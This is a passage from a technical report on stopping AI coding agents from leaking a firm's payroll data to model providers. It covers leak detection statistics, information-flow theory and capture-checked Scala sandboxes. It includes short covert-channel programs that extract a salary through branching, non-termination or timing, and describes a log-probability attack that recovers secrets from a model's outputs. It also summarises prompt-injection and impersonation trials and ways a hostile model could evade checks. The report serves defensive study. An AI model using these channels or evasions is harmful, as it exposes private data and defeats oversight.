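The list has to include the different forms a value might take. Willison (2026), a programmer who publishes transcripts of his coding sessions, wrote a tool that searches for known secrets and their common encodings. Xia and Park planted 852 credentials in 200 artificial sessions to test software that hides secrets from the provider. The full version let none through, but simpler versions let through 23.5% because some credentials were split into pieces or embedded in other text.

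Exact searches also miss paraphrases. For example, "Our only lawyer earns just under 120,000" reveals the Legal salary without containing any string on the list. The share of leaks missed varies greatly between studies. When Huang and colleagues had people read 200 outputs, they found useful private information in 100, of which exact matching had missed 12. In El Yagoubi and colleagues' validation test, searching for planted markers caught only 8% of leaks. The difference may be that Huang's prompts mostly asked for the items themselves, while El Yagoubi's agents were describing records in their own words.

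El Yagoubi and colleagues raised their detection rate to 93.4% by adding pattern searches and a language model that judges whether a text reveals a private fact. Since the payroll is fake, the firm could even use a hosted model as the judge. But the combined method also flagged 4.8% of harmless texts. If 10 of 1,000 tasks leak and the method checks one text per task, it will find about nine leaks and raise about 48 false alarms, so someone has to read the flagged texts before the firm can report a rate.

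Some exact matches will be false alarms too. In a department of five, the median is one employee's exact salary, so the search will flag a figure that the firm's rule allows. The testers can avoid this by giving every larger department an even number of employees.

Two more checks take little effort. The testers should run `print(staff.head())` on purpose and confirm that the search detects the leak, since it would also find nothing if the recorder were broken. They should also note whether the agent finished each task, because an agent that gives up early has fewer chances to leak data.

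This kind of test suits an honest model. A hostile one could behave well whenever the data looked fake, or encode a salary in a form that a search would miss. Outsiders can also cause leaks through prompt injection. DeepSeek leaked nothing in Huang and colleagues' ordinary tasks but leaked in every trial when the prompts asked for disclosure. A test with only ordinary tasks would therefore have passed a workflow that any successful prompt injection could exploit.

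### What a clean test allows

Suppose the firm runs 131 tasks and finds no leaks. The true leak rate could still be well above zero, because a system that leaks occasionally may get through 131 tasks by luck. If each task leaks with probability p, independently of the others, the chance of no leaks in 131 tasks is (1 − p)^131. The usual 95% limit is the value of p at which that chance falls to 5%:

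(1 − p)^131 = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/131) ≈ 0.023

A leak rate of about 2.3% is therefore still compatible with the clean test. At that rate, the firm would have about 23 leaks in 1,000 tasks. The true rate may be much lower, but the test can't show that. Dividing three by the number of tasks gives a quick estimate of the highest leak rate compatible with a clean test.

| Tasks with no leaks | Highest leak rate compatible with the result, at 95% confidence | Leaks per 1,000 tasks at that rate |
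|---|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% | 95 |
| 131 | 2.3% | 23 |
| 299 | 1.0% | 10 |
| 1,000 | 0.3% | 3 |
| 2,995 | 0.1% | 1 |

One leak in 131 tasks would raise the limit to about 3.6%. The firm should count that leak in its result even if it fixes the cause, and then test the repaired system on new tasks.

These limits hold only if the search catches every leak. Otherwise, the firm has to divide the limit by the share of leaks the search catches. For 131 clean tasks, the limit rises only slightly, to 2.4%, if the search catches 93.4% of leaks, but to about 28% if it catches 8%. Improving the search can therefore lower the limit more than running hundreds of extra tasks.

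The tasks also have to differ. Huang and colleagues' 150 trials per setting were 30 prompts run five times each. If all 150 trials were independent, a zero in their table would be consistent with a leak rate of up to about 2%. But if a prompt that is safe once is nearly always safe, repeating it adds little information, and the upper limit for new prompts is closer to the 9.5% for 30 tasks. If the firm tested a request for the median salary 131 times, it would learn very little about what happens when the analyst asks for pay letters.

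The result applies only to the system the firm tested. A new model, a new tool or a change in what the harness returns can open a route for leaks that the old tests didn't cover, so the firm should keep the fake payroll and rerun the tasks after each such change.

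## Which leaks still matter when nobody intends them

Searching for planted salaries finds salaries that appear as text. But a program can also reveal something about a salary without printing it, for example by printing "eligible" only for people who earn less than 40,000, or by running longer when someone earns more. Preventing every such leak is difficult and would block many useful programs, so the firm needs to know which ones an honest model is likely to cause by accident.

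*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who runs someone else's program on private data and wants to stop it from passing the data to the program's owner. If the program gives wrong answers, the customer has evidence for a complaint, but a leak usually leaves no trace. Lampson listed the routes he could think of. The program could simply write the data to a file in the owner's directory, or it could encode some of the data in the bill for the service, which the owner has to see. It could also vary how heavily it uses the machine, so that a second program can read the data from the changes in speed. Lampson called this last route a *covert channel*, because the load on a machine is not meant to carry information.

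The output of the analyst's program resembles Lampson's bill because the provider has to receive some of it, and the provider's model wrote the code that determines its contents.

### A definition of leaking nothing

*Noninterference* is the property that changing the private inputs never changes what an outsider observes. Write P(l, h) for everything the outsider observes when program P runs on public input l and private input h. The program satisfies noninterference if, for every l and every pair h₁ and h₂:

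P(l, h₁) = P(l, h₂)

For the analyst, l is her question and the column names, and h is the payroll. Finding two payrolls that produce different observations is enough to show that a program fails.

The more the definition assumes an outsider can observe, the stricter it is. A common version, used in *Explicit Secrecy* (Schoepe, Balliu and colleagues, 2016), compares the outputs of two runs only if both finish. A stricter version assumes the outsider can also observe whether the program finishes, and a still stricter one adds how long it takes.

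The median program fails even the loosest version, because raising the Legal salary from 118,000 to 119,000 changes what it prints. Almost any useful analysis of the payroll would fail too. The firm therefore needs *declassification*, a deliberate decision to release something derived from private data. Let R(h) be the figures that its rule permits, which are the medians for departments of at least five people. The firm can then require only that:

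if R(h₁) = R(h₂), then P(l, h₁) = P(l, h₂)

A program that meets this condition reveals nothing beyond the permitted figures. The median program still fails because of Legal, but passes once it leaves out the small departments.

A hostile program could try to disguise a forbidden figure as a permitted one:

```python
staff["annual_pay"] = staff.loc[7, "annual_pay"]
print(staff.groupby("department")["annual_pay"].median())
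```

The first line sets everyone's pay to one employee's salary, so every median equals that salary. An honest model has no reason to write this line. The program fails the condition above because R(h) refers to the original payroll, but it would pass a check that only tests whether each printed number came from the median function. Bastys, Piessens and Sabelfeld (2018) give a similar example with averages in *Prudent Design Principles for Information Flow Control*, and note that their JavaScript tool accepts it.

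### Four ways to reveal something about a salary

In the programs below, `salary` is the pay of the firm's only lawyer. The simplest leak is an *explicit flow*, which copies private data into an output:

```python
print(salary)
```

In *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, Denning and Denning (1977) call a flow explicit when the operations that produce it don't depend on the private value. For example, the same `print` statement discloses the value whether it is 118,000 or 52,000. Adding a 3% rise before printing wouldn't protect the value, since anyone who knows the formula can reverse it.

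In an *implicit flow*, the private value decides which part of the program runs:

```python
if salary > 100000:
    print("upper band")
else:
    print("lower band")
```

The provider's model wrote both printed texts as constants, but a provider that sees which one was printed learns whether the salary is above or below 100,000.

A program can reveal the same fact by failing to finish:

```python
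while salary > 100000:
    pass
print("finished")
```

It can also finish late:

```python
if salary > 100000:
    time.sleep(5)
print("finished")
```

The provider knows when it sent the program and when the result came back, so it can notice a five-second delay.

Denning and Denning showed how a compiler could check for explicit and implicit flows before a program runs. No such check can be exact, because deciding exactly which programs leak would solve the halting problem, which is impossible. Their method therefore rejects some harmless programs, including ones whose only forbidden line can never run. They left leaks through running time and physical signals, such as power consumption, to other mechanisms.

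They also had trouble with crashes. In one of their examples, a program repeatedly adds a private number to a total and prints a public counter after each addition. It crashes when the total no longer fits in the computer's register. With a 32-bit register, which holds numbers up to 2,147,483,647, a salary of 118,000 would make 18,199 the last counter value printed. Dividing the maximum by 18,199 gives almost exactly 118,000, and only seven whole-number salaries would have stopped the program at that point.

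Honest code can leak data when it reports its progress. Suppose a program prints a running count of the employees it has processed and stops with an error after number 412. The provider then knows that the 413th entry is unusual, even if the harness removes the error message.

### Counting what each program gives away

One *bit* is the information in the answer to a yes/no question whose two answers are equally likely. If every salary is a whole number below 2^17 (131,072), 17 bits are enough to identify any salary exactly. A provider that already knows roughly what lawyers earn needs fewer bits.

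Seventeen yes/no answers can deliver those 17 bits if the program chooses its questions well:

```python
low, high = 0, 131072
while high - low > 1:
    middle = (low + high) // 2
    if salary >= middle:
        low = middle
    else:
        high = middle
print(low)
```

The program first checks whether the salary is at least 65,536. Each comparison halves the remaining range, so after 17 of them only one value is left, and `low` equals the salary. For 118,000, the first five results are yes, yes, yes, no and no.

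Honest programs ask questions for other reasons. Suppose the firm offers travel loans to employees who earn less than 40,000, and the analyst wants to know who qualifies:

```python
for salary in staff["annual_pay"]:
    print("eligible" if salary < 40000 else "not eligible")
```

Each line reveals at most one bit about one employee, so lines for 500 employees reveal at most 500 bits, as much information as 29 complete salaries. The total is often lower because the answers are partly predictable. If one employee in ten is eligible, each answer carries about 0.47 bits on average, for a total of about 235 bits.

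A program with k possible outputs reveals at most log₂ k bits on average. If the analyst only needs the number of eligible employees, the output has 501 possible values and reveals less than 9 bits.

| What the program prints | Most it reveals about one employee | Most it reveals about 500 employees |
|---|---|---|
| Every salary | 17 bits | 8,500 bits |
| The result of 17 chosen comparisons for each salary | 17 bits | 8,500 bits |
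| One of four pay bands for each employee | 2 bits | 1,000 bits |
| One eligibility result for each employee | 1 bit | 500 bits |
| The number of eligible employees | 1 bit, usually far less | Under 9 bits |

A count of bits doesn't measure harm, however. The provider can't work out anyone's exact pay from the 500 eligibility results, but it can work out the lawyer's from 17 bits about her. Some secrets are only one bit long. If the payroll had a column showing who is about to lose their job, a single `if` could reveal that column's value for one employee.

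### How hostile code enlarges a small leak

The 17-question program gets past any check that follows only explicit flows, because it never copies `salary` into another variable and computes every value it stores from 0 and 131,072. Denning and Denning's method would reject the program, because the method also checks what a program does inside a branch that depends on private data.

A hostile author could respond by printing nothing inside the branch:

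```python
for guess in range(131072):
    print(guess)
    if guess == salary:
        while True:
            pass
```

The program prints each number as it counts upwards and gets stuck when it reaches the salary, so the last number printed before the harness stops it is the salary. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues (2008) encoded a program of this form for three established tools, Jif, FlowCaml and the SPARK Examiner, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*. Such tools accept it because the printing doesn't depend on the secret, and the branch that does depend on it prints nothing. Researchers had often defended this leniency by saying that a program reveals at most one bit by not finishing. That is true if the program prints only at the end, but not if it prints as it runs.

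In an experiment, Askarov and colleagues extracted a 32-bit number in under six seconds, using shared memory instead of printing to save time. A 17-bit salary has 32,768 times fewer possible values, so extracting it at that speed would take less than a fifth of a millisecond. Longer secrets are much safer, because the time doubles with every extra bit. The estimate for a credit card number was about 18 and a half days, and a 128-bit encryption key would take far too long to extract. They also proved that no program can do fundamentally better if its only leak is whether it finishes, so this limit protects the firm's keys but not its salaries.

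Leaking the salary through timing is even easier, since 17 programs that each pause if a particular binary digit is 1 would be enough. Lampson observed that noise wouldn't prevent this, because a suitable encoding gets the data through however small the effect on the machine, though perhaps slowly. Designers who expect hostile code therefore take these channels seriously. *A Verified Information-Flow Architecture* (2015) calls termination and timing "high-bandwidth channels" for malicious code that can read a secret directly.

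### Why explicit flows come first for an honest model

An explicit flow can copy a value of any size in one ordinary line of code. *Liberalizing Dependency* (2010) notes that attackers like explicit flows because a single method works for every value. An honest programmer can write such a line without thinking, as the nine routes out of the payroll showed. But revealing a whole salary through timing or an endless loop takes many well-chosen tests, and it is hard to imagine anyone writing those by accident.

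Russo, Sabelfeld and Li (2009), in *Implicit flows in malicious and nonmalicious code*, argued that implicit flows are often harmless in nonmalicious code because nobody can use them to extract secrets efficiently. For such code, they therefore combined a check for explicit flows with a search for particular patterns in the program's structure. Initial studies of industrial code for logging and data cleanup suggested that this method could give strong guarantees without too many false alarms.

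Schoepe and colleagues worked out what a check of explicit flows alone can guarantee. Their condition, *explicit secrecy*, requires that a run's assignments and outputs not depend on private data once the decisions that led to them are removed. In the program that prints the lawyer's pay band, this leaves only a line that prints a constant, so the program passes even though it reveals one bit of information about the lawyer's pay.

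The condition can also be too strict. A program that prints `salary` if the salary is 0, and prints 0 otherwise, always prints 0 and reveals nothing. It still fails the condition because one of its possible runs copies the salary into the output. A firm that checks only explicit flows will therefore miss some leaks and still get some false alarms.

Schoepe and colleagues' example of a website login shows why many people accept this trade-off. The program writes the user's whole request to a log, including the password, and then grants or refuses access. A check for explicit flows catches the logging of the password, which is a serious and common mistake. It doesn't flag the "access denied" message, which reveals that the password was wrong, but the website has to tell the user that anyway.

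*An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues, 2019) compared kinds of tracking on known security problems. Following explicit flows was enough to detect all the problems in trusted code. The problems it missed were in code that identifies visitors by their browser's characteristics or works out which sites they have visited. Staicu and colleagues attribute the difference to intent, since problems in trusted code come from programming errors. This supports the argument well, but people wrote the programs in the study, and AI models may make different mistakes.

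Bastys and colleagues turned the argument into the design principle that a check should match how far one trusts the code. Someone who writes hostile code chooses which flows to exploit, so the check has to cover everything that person could observe. Code from a trusted author is less likely to contain the tricks needed to exploit those flows. However, Bastys and colleagues warn that hostile inputs can exploit weaknesses in trusted code. A prompt injection gives the firm a stronger reason for caution, because it can change the code itself.

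### Honest loops that reveal everything

The argument has a gap, because honest code sometimes does ask many questions about one private value. Suppose the analyst wants pay letters with the salary written in words, as on a cheque. The model might write:

```python
words = ""
for digit in str(salary):
    if digit == "0":
        words += "zero "
    elif digit == "1":
        words += "one "
    # and so on, up to nine
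print(words)
```

For the lawyer, this prints "one one eight zero zero zero". The program adds only constant text to `words`, so a check that ignores branches does not flag the result as private. The program is a reasonable way to do the job, and the model did not write it to leak data.

Like the 17-question search, this program branches on private data inside a loop. A branch outside a loop reveals at most one bit each time it runs, but a loop can repeat the branch until it has revealed all the data. For honest code, the firm could therefore check explicit flows everywhere and also flag branches on private data inside loops. This would also flag the travel-loan program, probably rightly, because it prints something about each of 500 people. Someone could then decide whether the provider needs the list or only the total.

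Yes/no fields need stricter treatment. The firm should flag every branch that depends on the column showing who is about to lose their job, even outside a loop. If it assumes the model is honest, it can reasonably ignore timing leaks.

### When a rejected model tries again

Harnesses usually tell a model why its program failed and let it try again. This weakens the case for simple checks, because each new attempt is another chance for the check to accept a program it should reject.

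Suppose a fraction q of the model's attempts are safe and the rest would leak. The check accepts all the safe programs but also misses a fraction m of the leaking ones. If the attempts are independent and the model continues until one passes, the chance that the accepted program leaks is:

(1 − q)m / (q + (1 − q)m)

Suppose a check misses 5% of leaking programs, and the model retries until a program passes. If half of the model's attempts are safe, the chance of a leak is 4.8%, compared with 2.5% with a single attempt. If only one attempt in 20 is safe, the chance is 49%, compared with 4.75%. Retrying is therefore most dangerous when a safe program is hard to write.

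Real attempts aren't independent, because a model that reads the reason for a rejection changes its next program. The new program may be safe, or it may use code that the check doesn't understand. For example, a task may depend on how salaries are formatted in the payroll. The check rejects a program that prints the first few, so the model writes a loop that reports whether each character is a digit. If the task also depends on which characters appear, the model can branch on each one, which makes the program very similar to the one for pay letters. With a hosted model, this is already a leak, even if the model was only inspecting the data to do its job.

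Models do use this kind of feedback. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes a loop that returns error messages to a model until its code has valid syntax, for at most five rounds. Asked for a factorial function in their small programming language, the model succeeded in the third round. The agents that Odersky and colleagues tested also read compiler errors and tried again. These examples involve ordinary repairs, so they don't show how often an honest model accidentally finds a gap in a security check, which the firm would have to measure itself.

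A rejection can also carry private data. If the check examines only the program's code, its result is the same for every payroll and reveals nothing about anyone's pay. But if the harness stops a program while it is running, the reason may depend on a salary, in which case stopping leaks a little information about it. Garby and colleagues criticise CaMeL, a system that tracks data in agents' programs, for running its checks inside a retry loop that CaMeL doesn't track. An attacker could repeat a carefully designed program, learn one bit each time from whether CaMeL blocked it, and work out a salary in seventeen runs.

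An honest model wouldn't design its attempts to extract a salary, so a low limit on retries helps a lot. If the harness allows five attempts and reports only whether it blocked each one, those reports reveal at most five bits. The firm should also review programs that passed after an earlier rejection, since gaps in the check are most likely to show up there. A cap on retries wouldn't solve the harder problem of a model that deliberately works around its limits.

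### A model that has already seen the secret

So far, the model has written code without seeing the salaries. Once a salary is in its context, the model can reveal information about that salary while doing an unrelated task.

In *LLMs Leak Secrets Through Unrelated Outputs*, Bhardwaj, Kaya and colleagues (2026) gave a small open model, Qwen3-8B, a four-digit PIN and told it not to reveal the PIN. They then asked it for ten random even numbers between 0 and 9,999. A language model generates each piece of text according to probabilities that depend on its whole context, so the PIN slightly changed which numbers the model was likely to produce.

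Bhardwaj and colleagues assumed an attacker with a lot of knowledge. This attacker has the model's weights, which are the learned numbers that determine its behaviour, and knows the wording of the prompt or something close to it. The attacker can therefore put any candidate PIN into the prompt and calculate how likely the model would have been to write the lists it actually wrote. The score of a candidate s is:

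score(s) = the sum, over all observed lists, of the average log-probability of the list's tokens when the prompt contains s

Tokens are the small pieces of text the model produces one at a time. The attacker's best guess is the highest-scoring candidate.

In the first test, the attacker saw one list and had to choose between four possible PINs or no PIN. The attacker guessed right in 193 of 250 trials (77.2%), compared with 20% by chance. Accuracy stayed above 73% when the researchers removed every list containing the PIN, a rearrangement of its digits, or a number that differed from it in one digit, so the model hadn't simply copied the PIN.

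The second test allowed all 10,000 PINs, and the attacker used about 20 lists for each, all filtered in the same way. The attacker recovered 24 of 50 PINs exactly and had the right PIN among the top five guesses for 36. With only 50 PINs, the 95% confidence interval for exact recovery is wide, from 35% to 61%.

Warning the model in the prompt that someone would audit its output for leaks helped only partly. In a repeat of the five-way test, the warning lowered accuracy from 79.2% to 44.0%, still more than twice the rate expected by chance.

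The attack was weaker on other models. It could still pick out a PIN from a small set of candidates, but when the attacker had to search all 10,000, it recovered one of six PINs from Phi-3.5-Mini and none of six from OLMo-2-7B. Scoring Qwen's lists with either of those models worked much less well than scoring them with Qwen itself, so an attacker needs the model that generated them. The output also has to vary, because lists of numbers from 1 to 10 were nearly identical whatever the PIN was, and accuracy fell to chance.

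If the Legal salary is in a hosted model's context, the provider already has it and learns nothing new from this attack. The attack matters more if the firm runs a local model on the payroll and sends some of the model's output to the provider. Many local models have public weights, so the provider could run the same one. The local model might then leak the salary unintentionally, but the provider would have to try to recover it. The firm's threat model covers that, since the firm assumes the provider may keep and read whatever it receives.

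The practical danger for the payroll still looks small. The experiment used one short secret in a very short prompt, and the attacker needed many outputs with random-looking numbers. Nobody has shown that the method works for one salary among 500, or for ordinary prose. But the experiment does show that it is unsafe to search a local model's output for salaries and send it on if the search finds none. Garby and colleagues build a safer rule into their language, where a conversation carries the labels of everything anyone has put into it. Under that rule, the random numbers would be as confidential as the PIN.

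## Checking generated code before it runs

LACUNA and TACIT have the model write Scala because Scala's compiler can reject a leaking program before it runs, whereas Python reports most mistakes only when the faulty line runs. The Scala compiler works out the type of every value, such as whole number, text or list, and rejects programs in which the types don't fit together.

### What an ordinary type check stops

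LACUNA runs programs that contain gaps for the model to fill. A gap looks like `agent[String]("Write a status message")`, where `String` means the program expects text. When the program reaches the gap, LACUNA sends the model the request, the expected type, the surrounding code, and the names and types of the available variables. The compiler checks the model's reply as if a programmer had typed it at that spot. If the reply fails the check, LACUNA sends the compiler's errors to the model and requests another reply, up to a set limit.

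Suppose the surrounding program has stored the lawyer's pay in a variable called `salary` and now needs a status message. The compiler would reject a reply that uses a variable called `wage`, because none exists. It would also reject a reply that ends with a number instead of text.

If any line fails the check, none of the code runs. Zhao and colleagues show this with a reply that subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program expects a number. The balance stays at 100. In the salary task, a reply that sent an e-mail on its first line and had a type error on its second would send nothing, whereas Python would send the e-mail and then stop. The check catches only errors that the compiler can find, so a pay cell with a note in it can still stop an accepted program after its earlier lines have taken effect.

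Zhao and colleagues tested the checker on about 400 combinations of surrounding program and reply, with no model involved, and it behaved as intended on all of them. But the following reply is also correct by its rules:

```scala
println(salary)
"Finished reading the payroll"
```

The variable exists, `println` accepts any value, and the last line is text. The compiler accepts the reply, and a harness that returns printed output sends the salary to the provider. LACUNA also has a less obvious route, because the model's code may contain further gaps:

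```scala
agent[String](s"Write a pay letter for someone who earns $salary")
```

Scala replaces `$salary` with the figure, and LACUNA sends the finished request to the model. An honest model could easily write either line. `salary` has type `Int`, a whole number, which gives the compiler no information about who may see the figure.

### Recording what a function can do

Scala 3 has an experimental feature called *capture checking*, which adds information about effects to types. The type of a value then includes a *capture set*, a list of the capabilities that the value may use. For example, suppose `f` is a capability for writing to a file. A function that writes text to it has this type:

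```scala
String ->{f} Unit
```

The function takes text, may use `f`, and returns no useful value (`Unit`). A function that only converts text to capitals has the type `String -> String`, with no capture set. It is a *pure function*, meaning it computes a result and has no outside effect. The compiler works out most capture sets. A set must include every capability the function uses, and may include some it never uses.

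TACIT uses capture sets to protect private files. When a program reads a file that the firm has marked as private, it gets the contents inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The program can't take the contents out. It can only give the wrapper a function to apply to them:

```scala
def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The thin arrow means that `map` accepts only pure functions. A function that prints, writes a file or contacts a website needs a capability, so it has the wrong type. The result of `map` is wrapped again, so a program can process a salary in many steps without unwrapping it.

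This also deals with implicit flows, because a program can only branch on a salary inside `map`, and the wrapper then covers whatever the branch produces. The program that spells out salaries digit by digit would compile and run, but its output would remain wrapped, as would the result of the 17-question search. The wrapper is useful against both honest mistakes and deliberate leaks.

### The salary task in TACIT

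The firm marks `salaries.csv` as classified, and the analyst asks for the median pay in each department. The model writes an ordinary pure function, `medians`, which takes the file's text and returns the figures. It then writes:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/payroll") {
  val payroll = readClassified("/payroll/salaries.csv")
  val result = payroll.map(text => medians(text))
  println(result)
}
```

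The compiler accepts this program. The analyst sees the four medians, and the model sees only `Classified(****)`.

Now suppose the model wants to look at the start of the file first:

```scala
payroll.map { text =>
  println(text.take(200))
}
```

The compiler rejects this program because `println` needs a capability to produce output. The function passed to `map` captures that capability, but `map` accepts only functions with an empty capture set. The program has not yet read the payroll when the model receives the error. Odersky and colleagues show the same kind of compiler error from their benchmark, where an agent's program tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`.

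The model can fix the error by printing the wrapped result instead:

```scala
println(payroll.map(text => text.take(200)))
```

This compiles, and the analyst sees the first 200 characters. The model still has no information about how the salaries are formatted, which the code was meant to provide.

TACIT is also stricter than the firm's rule, which lets the provider have medians for departments of at least five people. The wrapper's method for revealing its contents requires a permission that the agent doesn't have. To release the permitted medians, the firm would have to write a trusted function that leaves out small departments and returns the other departments' medians unwrapped. That function should read the payroll file itself, because a hostile model could otherwise give it the altered payroll described earlier, in which every median equals one person's salary. For an honest model,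 a function that accepts any wrapped payroll would be enough.

### Access to files and websites

The block that starts with `requestFileSystem("/payroll")` gives the program access to one folder until the block ends. If the program tries to access a path outside that folder, TACIT denies access at runtime. Similar blocks grant access to named commands and named web hosts. Opening any of these blocks requires the output capability, so a program can't open one inside `map`.

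These limits help with honest mistakes, such as reading the wrong folder. The compiler also prevents the program from keeping a file handle after the block ends, though this rule matters less for an honest model. One agent that Odersky and colleagues tested broke the rule by returning a list of file handles from a block, probably because that was a convenient way to organise the code. Even a hostile model gains little from keeping a handle if it can open another block. The rule becomes useful when the surrounding program allows reading in one phase and sending in the next, as Zhao and colleagues suggest, because code from the first phase then can't pass its file access to the second.

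*TACIT*, a page on the agent-tool directory Glama, reproduces the project's newer documentation. It describes a function that posts a `Classified` value to a website and wraps the reply. The program names the permitted hosts in its own code, and the firm can set a second list that every host must also match. If the firm leaves that list unset, only the program's list applies, so a program appears able to send the whole wrapped payroll to any host it chooses and still pass the compiler's checks.

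An honest model might use this function to send the payroll to the charting company in the earlier example, and a hostile model could send it to its own server. The firm should therefore always set the second list and include only hosts that are allowed to receive everything the firm has marked as private.

### Printed output and error messages

TACIT's `println` sends one copy of its output to the model and another only to the user. The copies are identical except that the model's has asterisks in place of `Classified` values. This is the part of the design that matters most when the model is honest, because printing and logging caused nearly three quarters of the careless credential leaks that Chen and colleagues found in agent skills.

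In the newer version, TACIT writes the user's copy to a file whose location the firm has to set. If the firm doesn't set one, the analyst sees asterisks too. TACIT creates the file so that only its owner can read it, but the file holds an unprotected copy of every salary that a program has printed. The firm should delete it regularly and keep it out of shared folders.

Error messages are harder to control with types. *Safe Mode*, a page of Scala's documentation, explains that tracking every possible error would be too cumbersome, because something as common as dividing by zero or running out of memory can make a program fail. TACIT instead catches errors while the program runs and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap. This would keep the message about the lawyer's pay, "118000 until she leaves in May", from reaching the provider.

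An honest model needs this protection because its programs will often fail on untidy data. With a hostile model, TACIT also has to hide that an error occurred, since the model could write a program that fails only if the salary is above 100,000. In one set of tests, Odersky and colleagues hid both. If a function failed inside `map`, the run looked successful to the model and the user saw nothing. They therefore told the agents to return a short explanation instead of raising an error. The payroll analyst might then read "One pay cell contains text". The model would not see that message, so she would have to tell it about the problem herself without revealing what the cell says.

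### Safe mode

Scala lets programmers override its type system when they need to. For instance, a *cast* makes the compiler treat a value as if it had another type. After the compiler rejects the printing function above, a model could add a cast that declares the function pure, and the program would then compile and print the payroll. *Safe mode* removes such features from the code that an agent may write. Scala's documentation lists six restrictions:

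| Restriction | What a model could otherwise do | Does an honest model need it? |
|---|---|---|
| No unchecked casts or pattern matches | Declare a printing function pure | Yes, because a model may add a cast just to get rid of an error |
| Nothing from the `caps.unsafe` module | Turn off tracking for a value | Rarely |
| No `@unchecked` annotations | Suppress the compiler's checks | Sometimes, for the same reason as casts |
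| No runtime reflection | Find and call hidden parts of the program by name | Rarely |
| Capture checking always on | Use a capability that no type records | Yes, because the wrapper depends on it |
| Only global objects that are themselves safe | Read the payroll with Java's ordinary file functions | Yes |

The last restriction probably matters most for honest mistakes. Any model that has learned Scala has also learned Java's file functions, which would return the payroll as plain text without the wrapper.

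Haskell, another language with strict types, has a similar mode. GHC's *Safe Haskell* describes a program that runs an untrusted author's plugin and uses types to limit which files the plugin can touch. Without the safe mode, the author could use `unsafePerformIO` to present any action as a pure function. That would be a deliberate attack, and an honest model is unlikely to use such a function, except perhaps while trying to fix a compiler error.

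A programmer can exempt a trusted library from safe mode by marking it `@assumeSafe` and taking responsibility for checking it. Scala's documentation gives the example of a mail function that shows each message to the user and sends it only if she agrees. With such a function, the analyst in the salary task could notice the lawyer's pay before the e-mail reached the mail company. But she would have to read the message carefully, which becomes less likely as the number of messages grows.

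In March 2026, lampepfl's *TACIT*, the research group's project page, described a validator that enforced these restrictions by searching the model's code for forbidden patterns, because the compiler's safe mode was still under development. A pattern search should catch an honest model's use of forbidden names, since the model writes them in the usual way, but a hostile model could look for a spelling that the patterns miss. TACIT's newer version can use both the validator and the compiler's safe mode. The documentation describes safe mode as on by default in one place and as an optional addition in another, so the firm should turn it on explicitly.

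### What the attack trials measured

Odersky and colleagues tested the wrapper on a software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys, a database and confidential documents. They ran each of 12 user tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Some injections were disguised as tool errors that needed a password to fix, and others included complete Scala code that would read the secret files. Another 11 trials had no injection. In five, the user asked for secrets directly, and in the other six, the user posed as someone with authority, such as an administrator replacing passwords in an emergency.

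They ran all 131 trials with two models, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output. The table also shows how often the agents completed the 120 user tasks.

| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Secure trials, wrapped | 100% | 100% |
| Secure trials, not wrapped | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| Tasks completed, wrapped | 99.2% | 90.0% |
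| Tasks completed, not wrapped | 83.3% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet resisted every injection but leaked secrets in two of the trials where the user posed as someone with authority. MiniMax leaked secrets in three injection trials and in eight of the 11 other trials. With the wrapper, this difference between the models no longer mattered.

Every trial involved an injection or a user who asked for secrets, so these success rates don't measure how often an honest model leaks data by accident. To measure that, the researchers would have had to run the 12 ordinary tasks without any attack. The results without the wrapper may also understate what the providers received. If an agent read a key and then declined to repeat it, the trial presumably counted as secure, even though the key had reached the hosted model.

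The perfect scores are good evidence that TACIT's parts work together, but the argument for the design depends mainly on its type rules. As the earlier calculation showed, 131 clean trials alone can't rule out a failure rate of about 2%, and these trials reused the same 12 tasks and 10 injections. The project page from March reports the same results and names the pattern validator as the current mechanism, so the trials probably tested the validator and not the compiler's safe mode.

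Surprisingly, Sonnet completed more tasks with the wrapper than without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that this may be an artefact of the setup. When Sonnet detected an injection, it sometimes stopped to warn the user, and it often ran out of time or turns. The wrapper exposed it to fewer injections, which would explain part of the difference.

### The cost in completed tasks

Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT, which has agents write Scala, with ordinary tool calling, where the model requests one action at a time. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer-service conversations, TACIT did better with all three models tested in both areas, airlines and retail, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with ordinary tools.

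The τ²-bench tools returned customer records as ordinary data, so those results show that models can write Scala but don't test whether they can work with data they can't see. AgentDojo, a set of office, banking and travel tasks with planted injections, is a harder test because TACIT wrapped e-mails, messages, files and reviews. The table shows the share of tasks completed by TACIT, by LACUNA with capture checking, and by CaMeL, which tracks data while a program runs.

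| Model | Area | CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 63.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 56.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 42.9% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 63.6% |
| o4-mini-high | Banking | 62.5% | 59.0% | 66.0% |
| o4-mini-high | Workspace | 81.4% | 52.9% | 55.5% |
| o4-mini-high | Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% | 49.5% |
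| o4-mini-high | Travel | 74.3% | 68.6% | 71.4% |

TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL in six of the eight comparisons. Odersky and colleagues describe the two systems' results as comparable, which is fair for banking, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT's completion rate was 28.5 points lower on workspace tasks and 21 points lower on Slack tasks. TACIT had a large lead only on travel tasks with Gemini, where CaMeL almost always failed. The workspace results are probably the most relevant to the analyst, since those tasks involve reading files and writing e-mails.

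All three systems blocked nearly every attack in about 1,900 trials each. One attack succeeded against CaMeL, one against TACIT and eight against LACUNA. The TACIT case was harmless because the agent booked the right hotel and only quoted to the user an injected review recommending a different one. Zhao and colleagues connect LACUNA's eight failures to the limit mentioned earlier, the misuse of access that the task requires.

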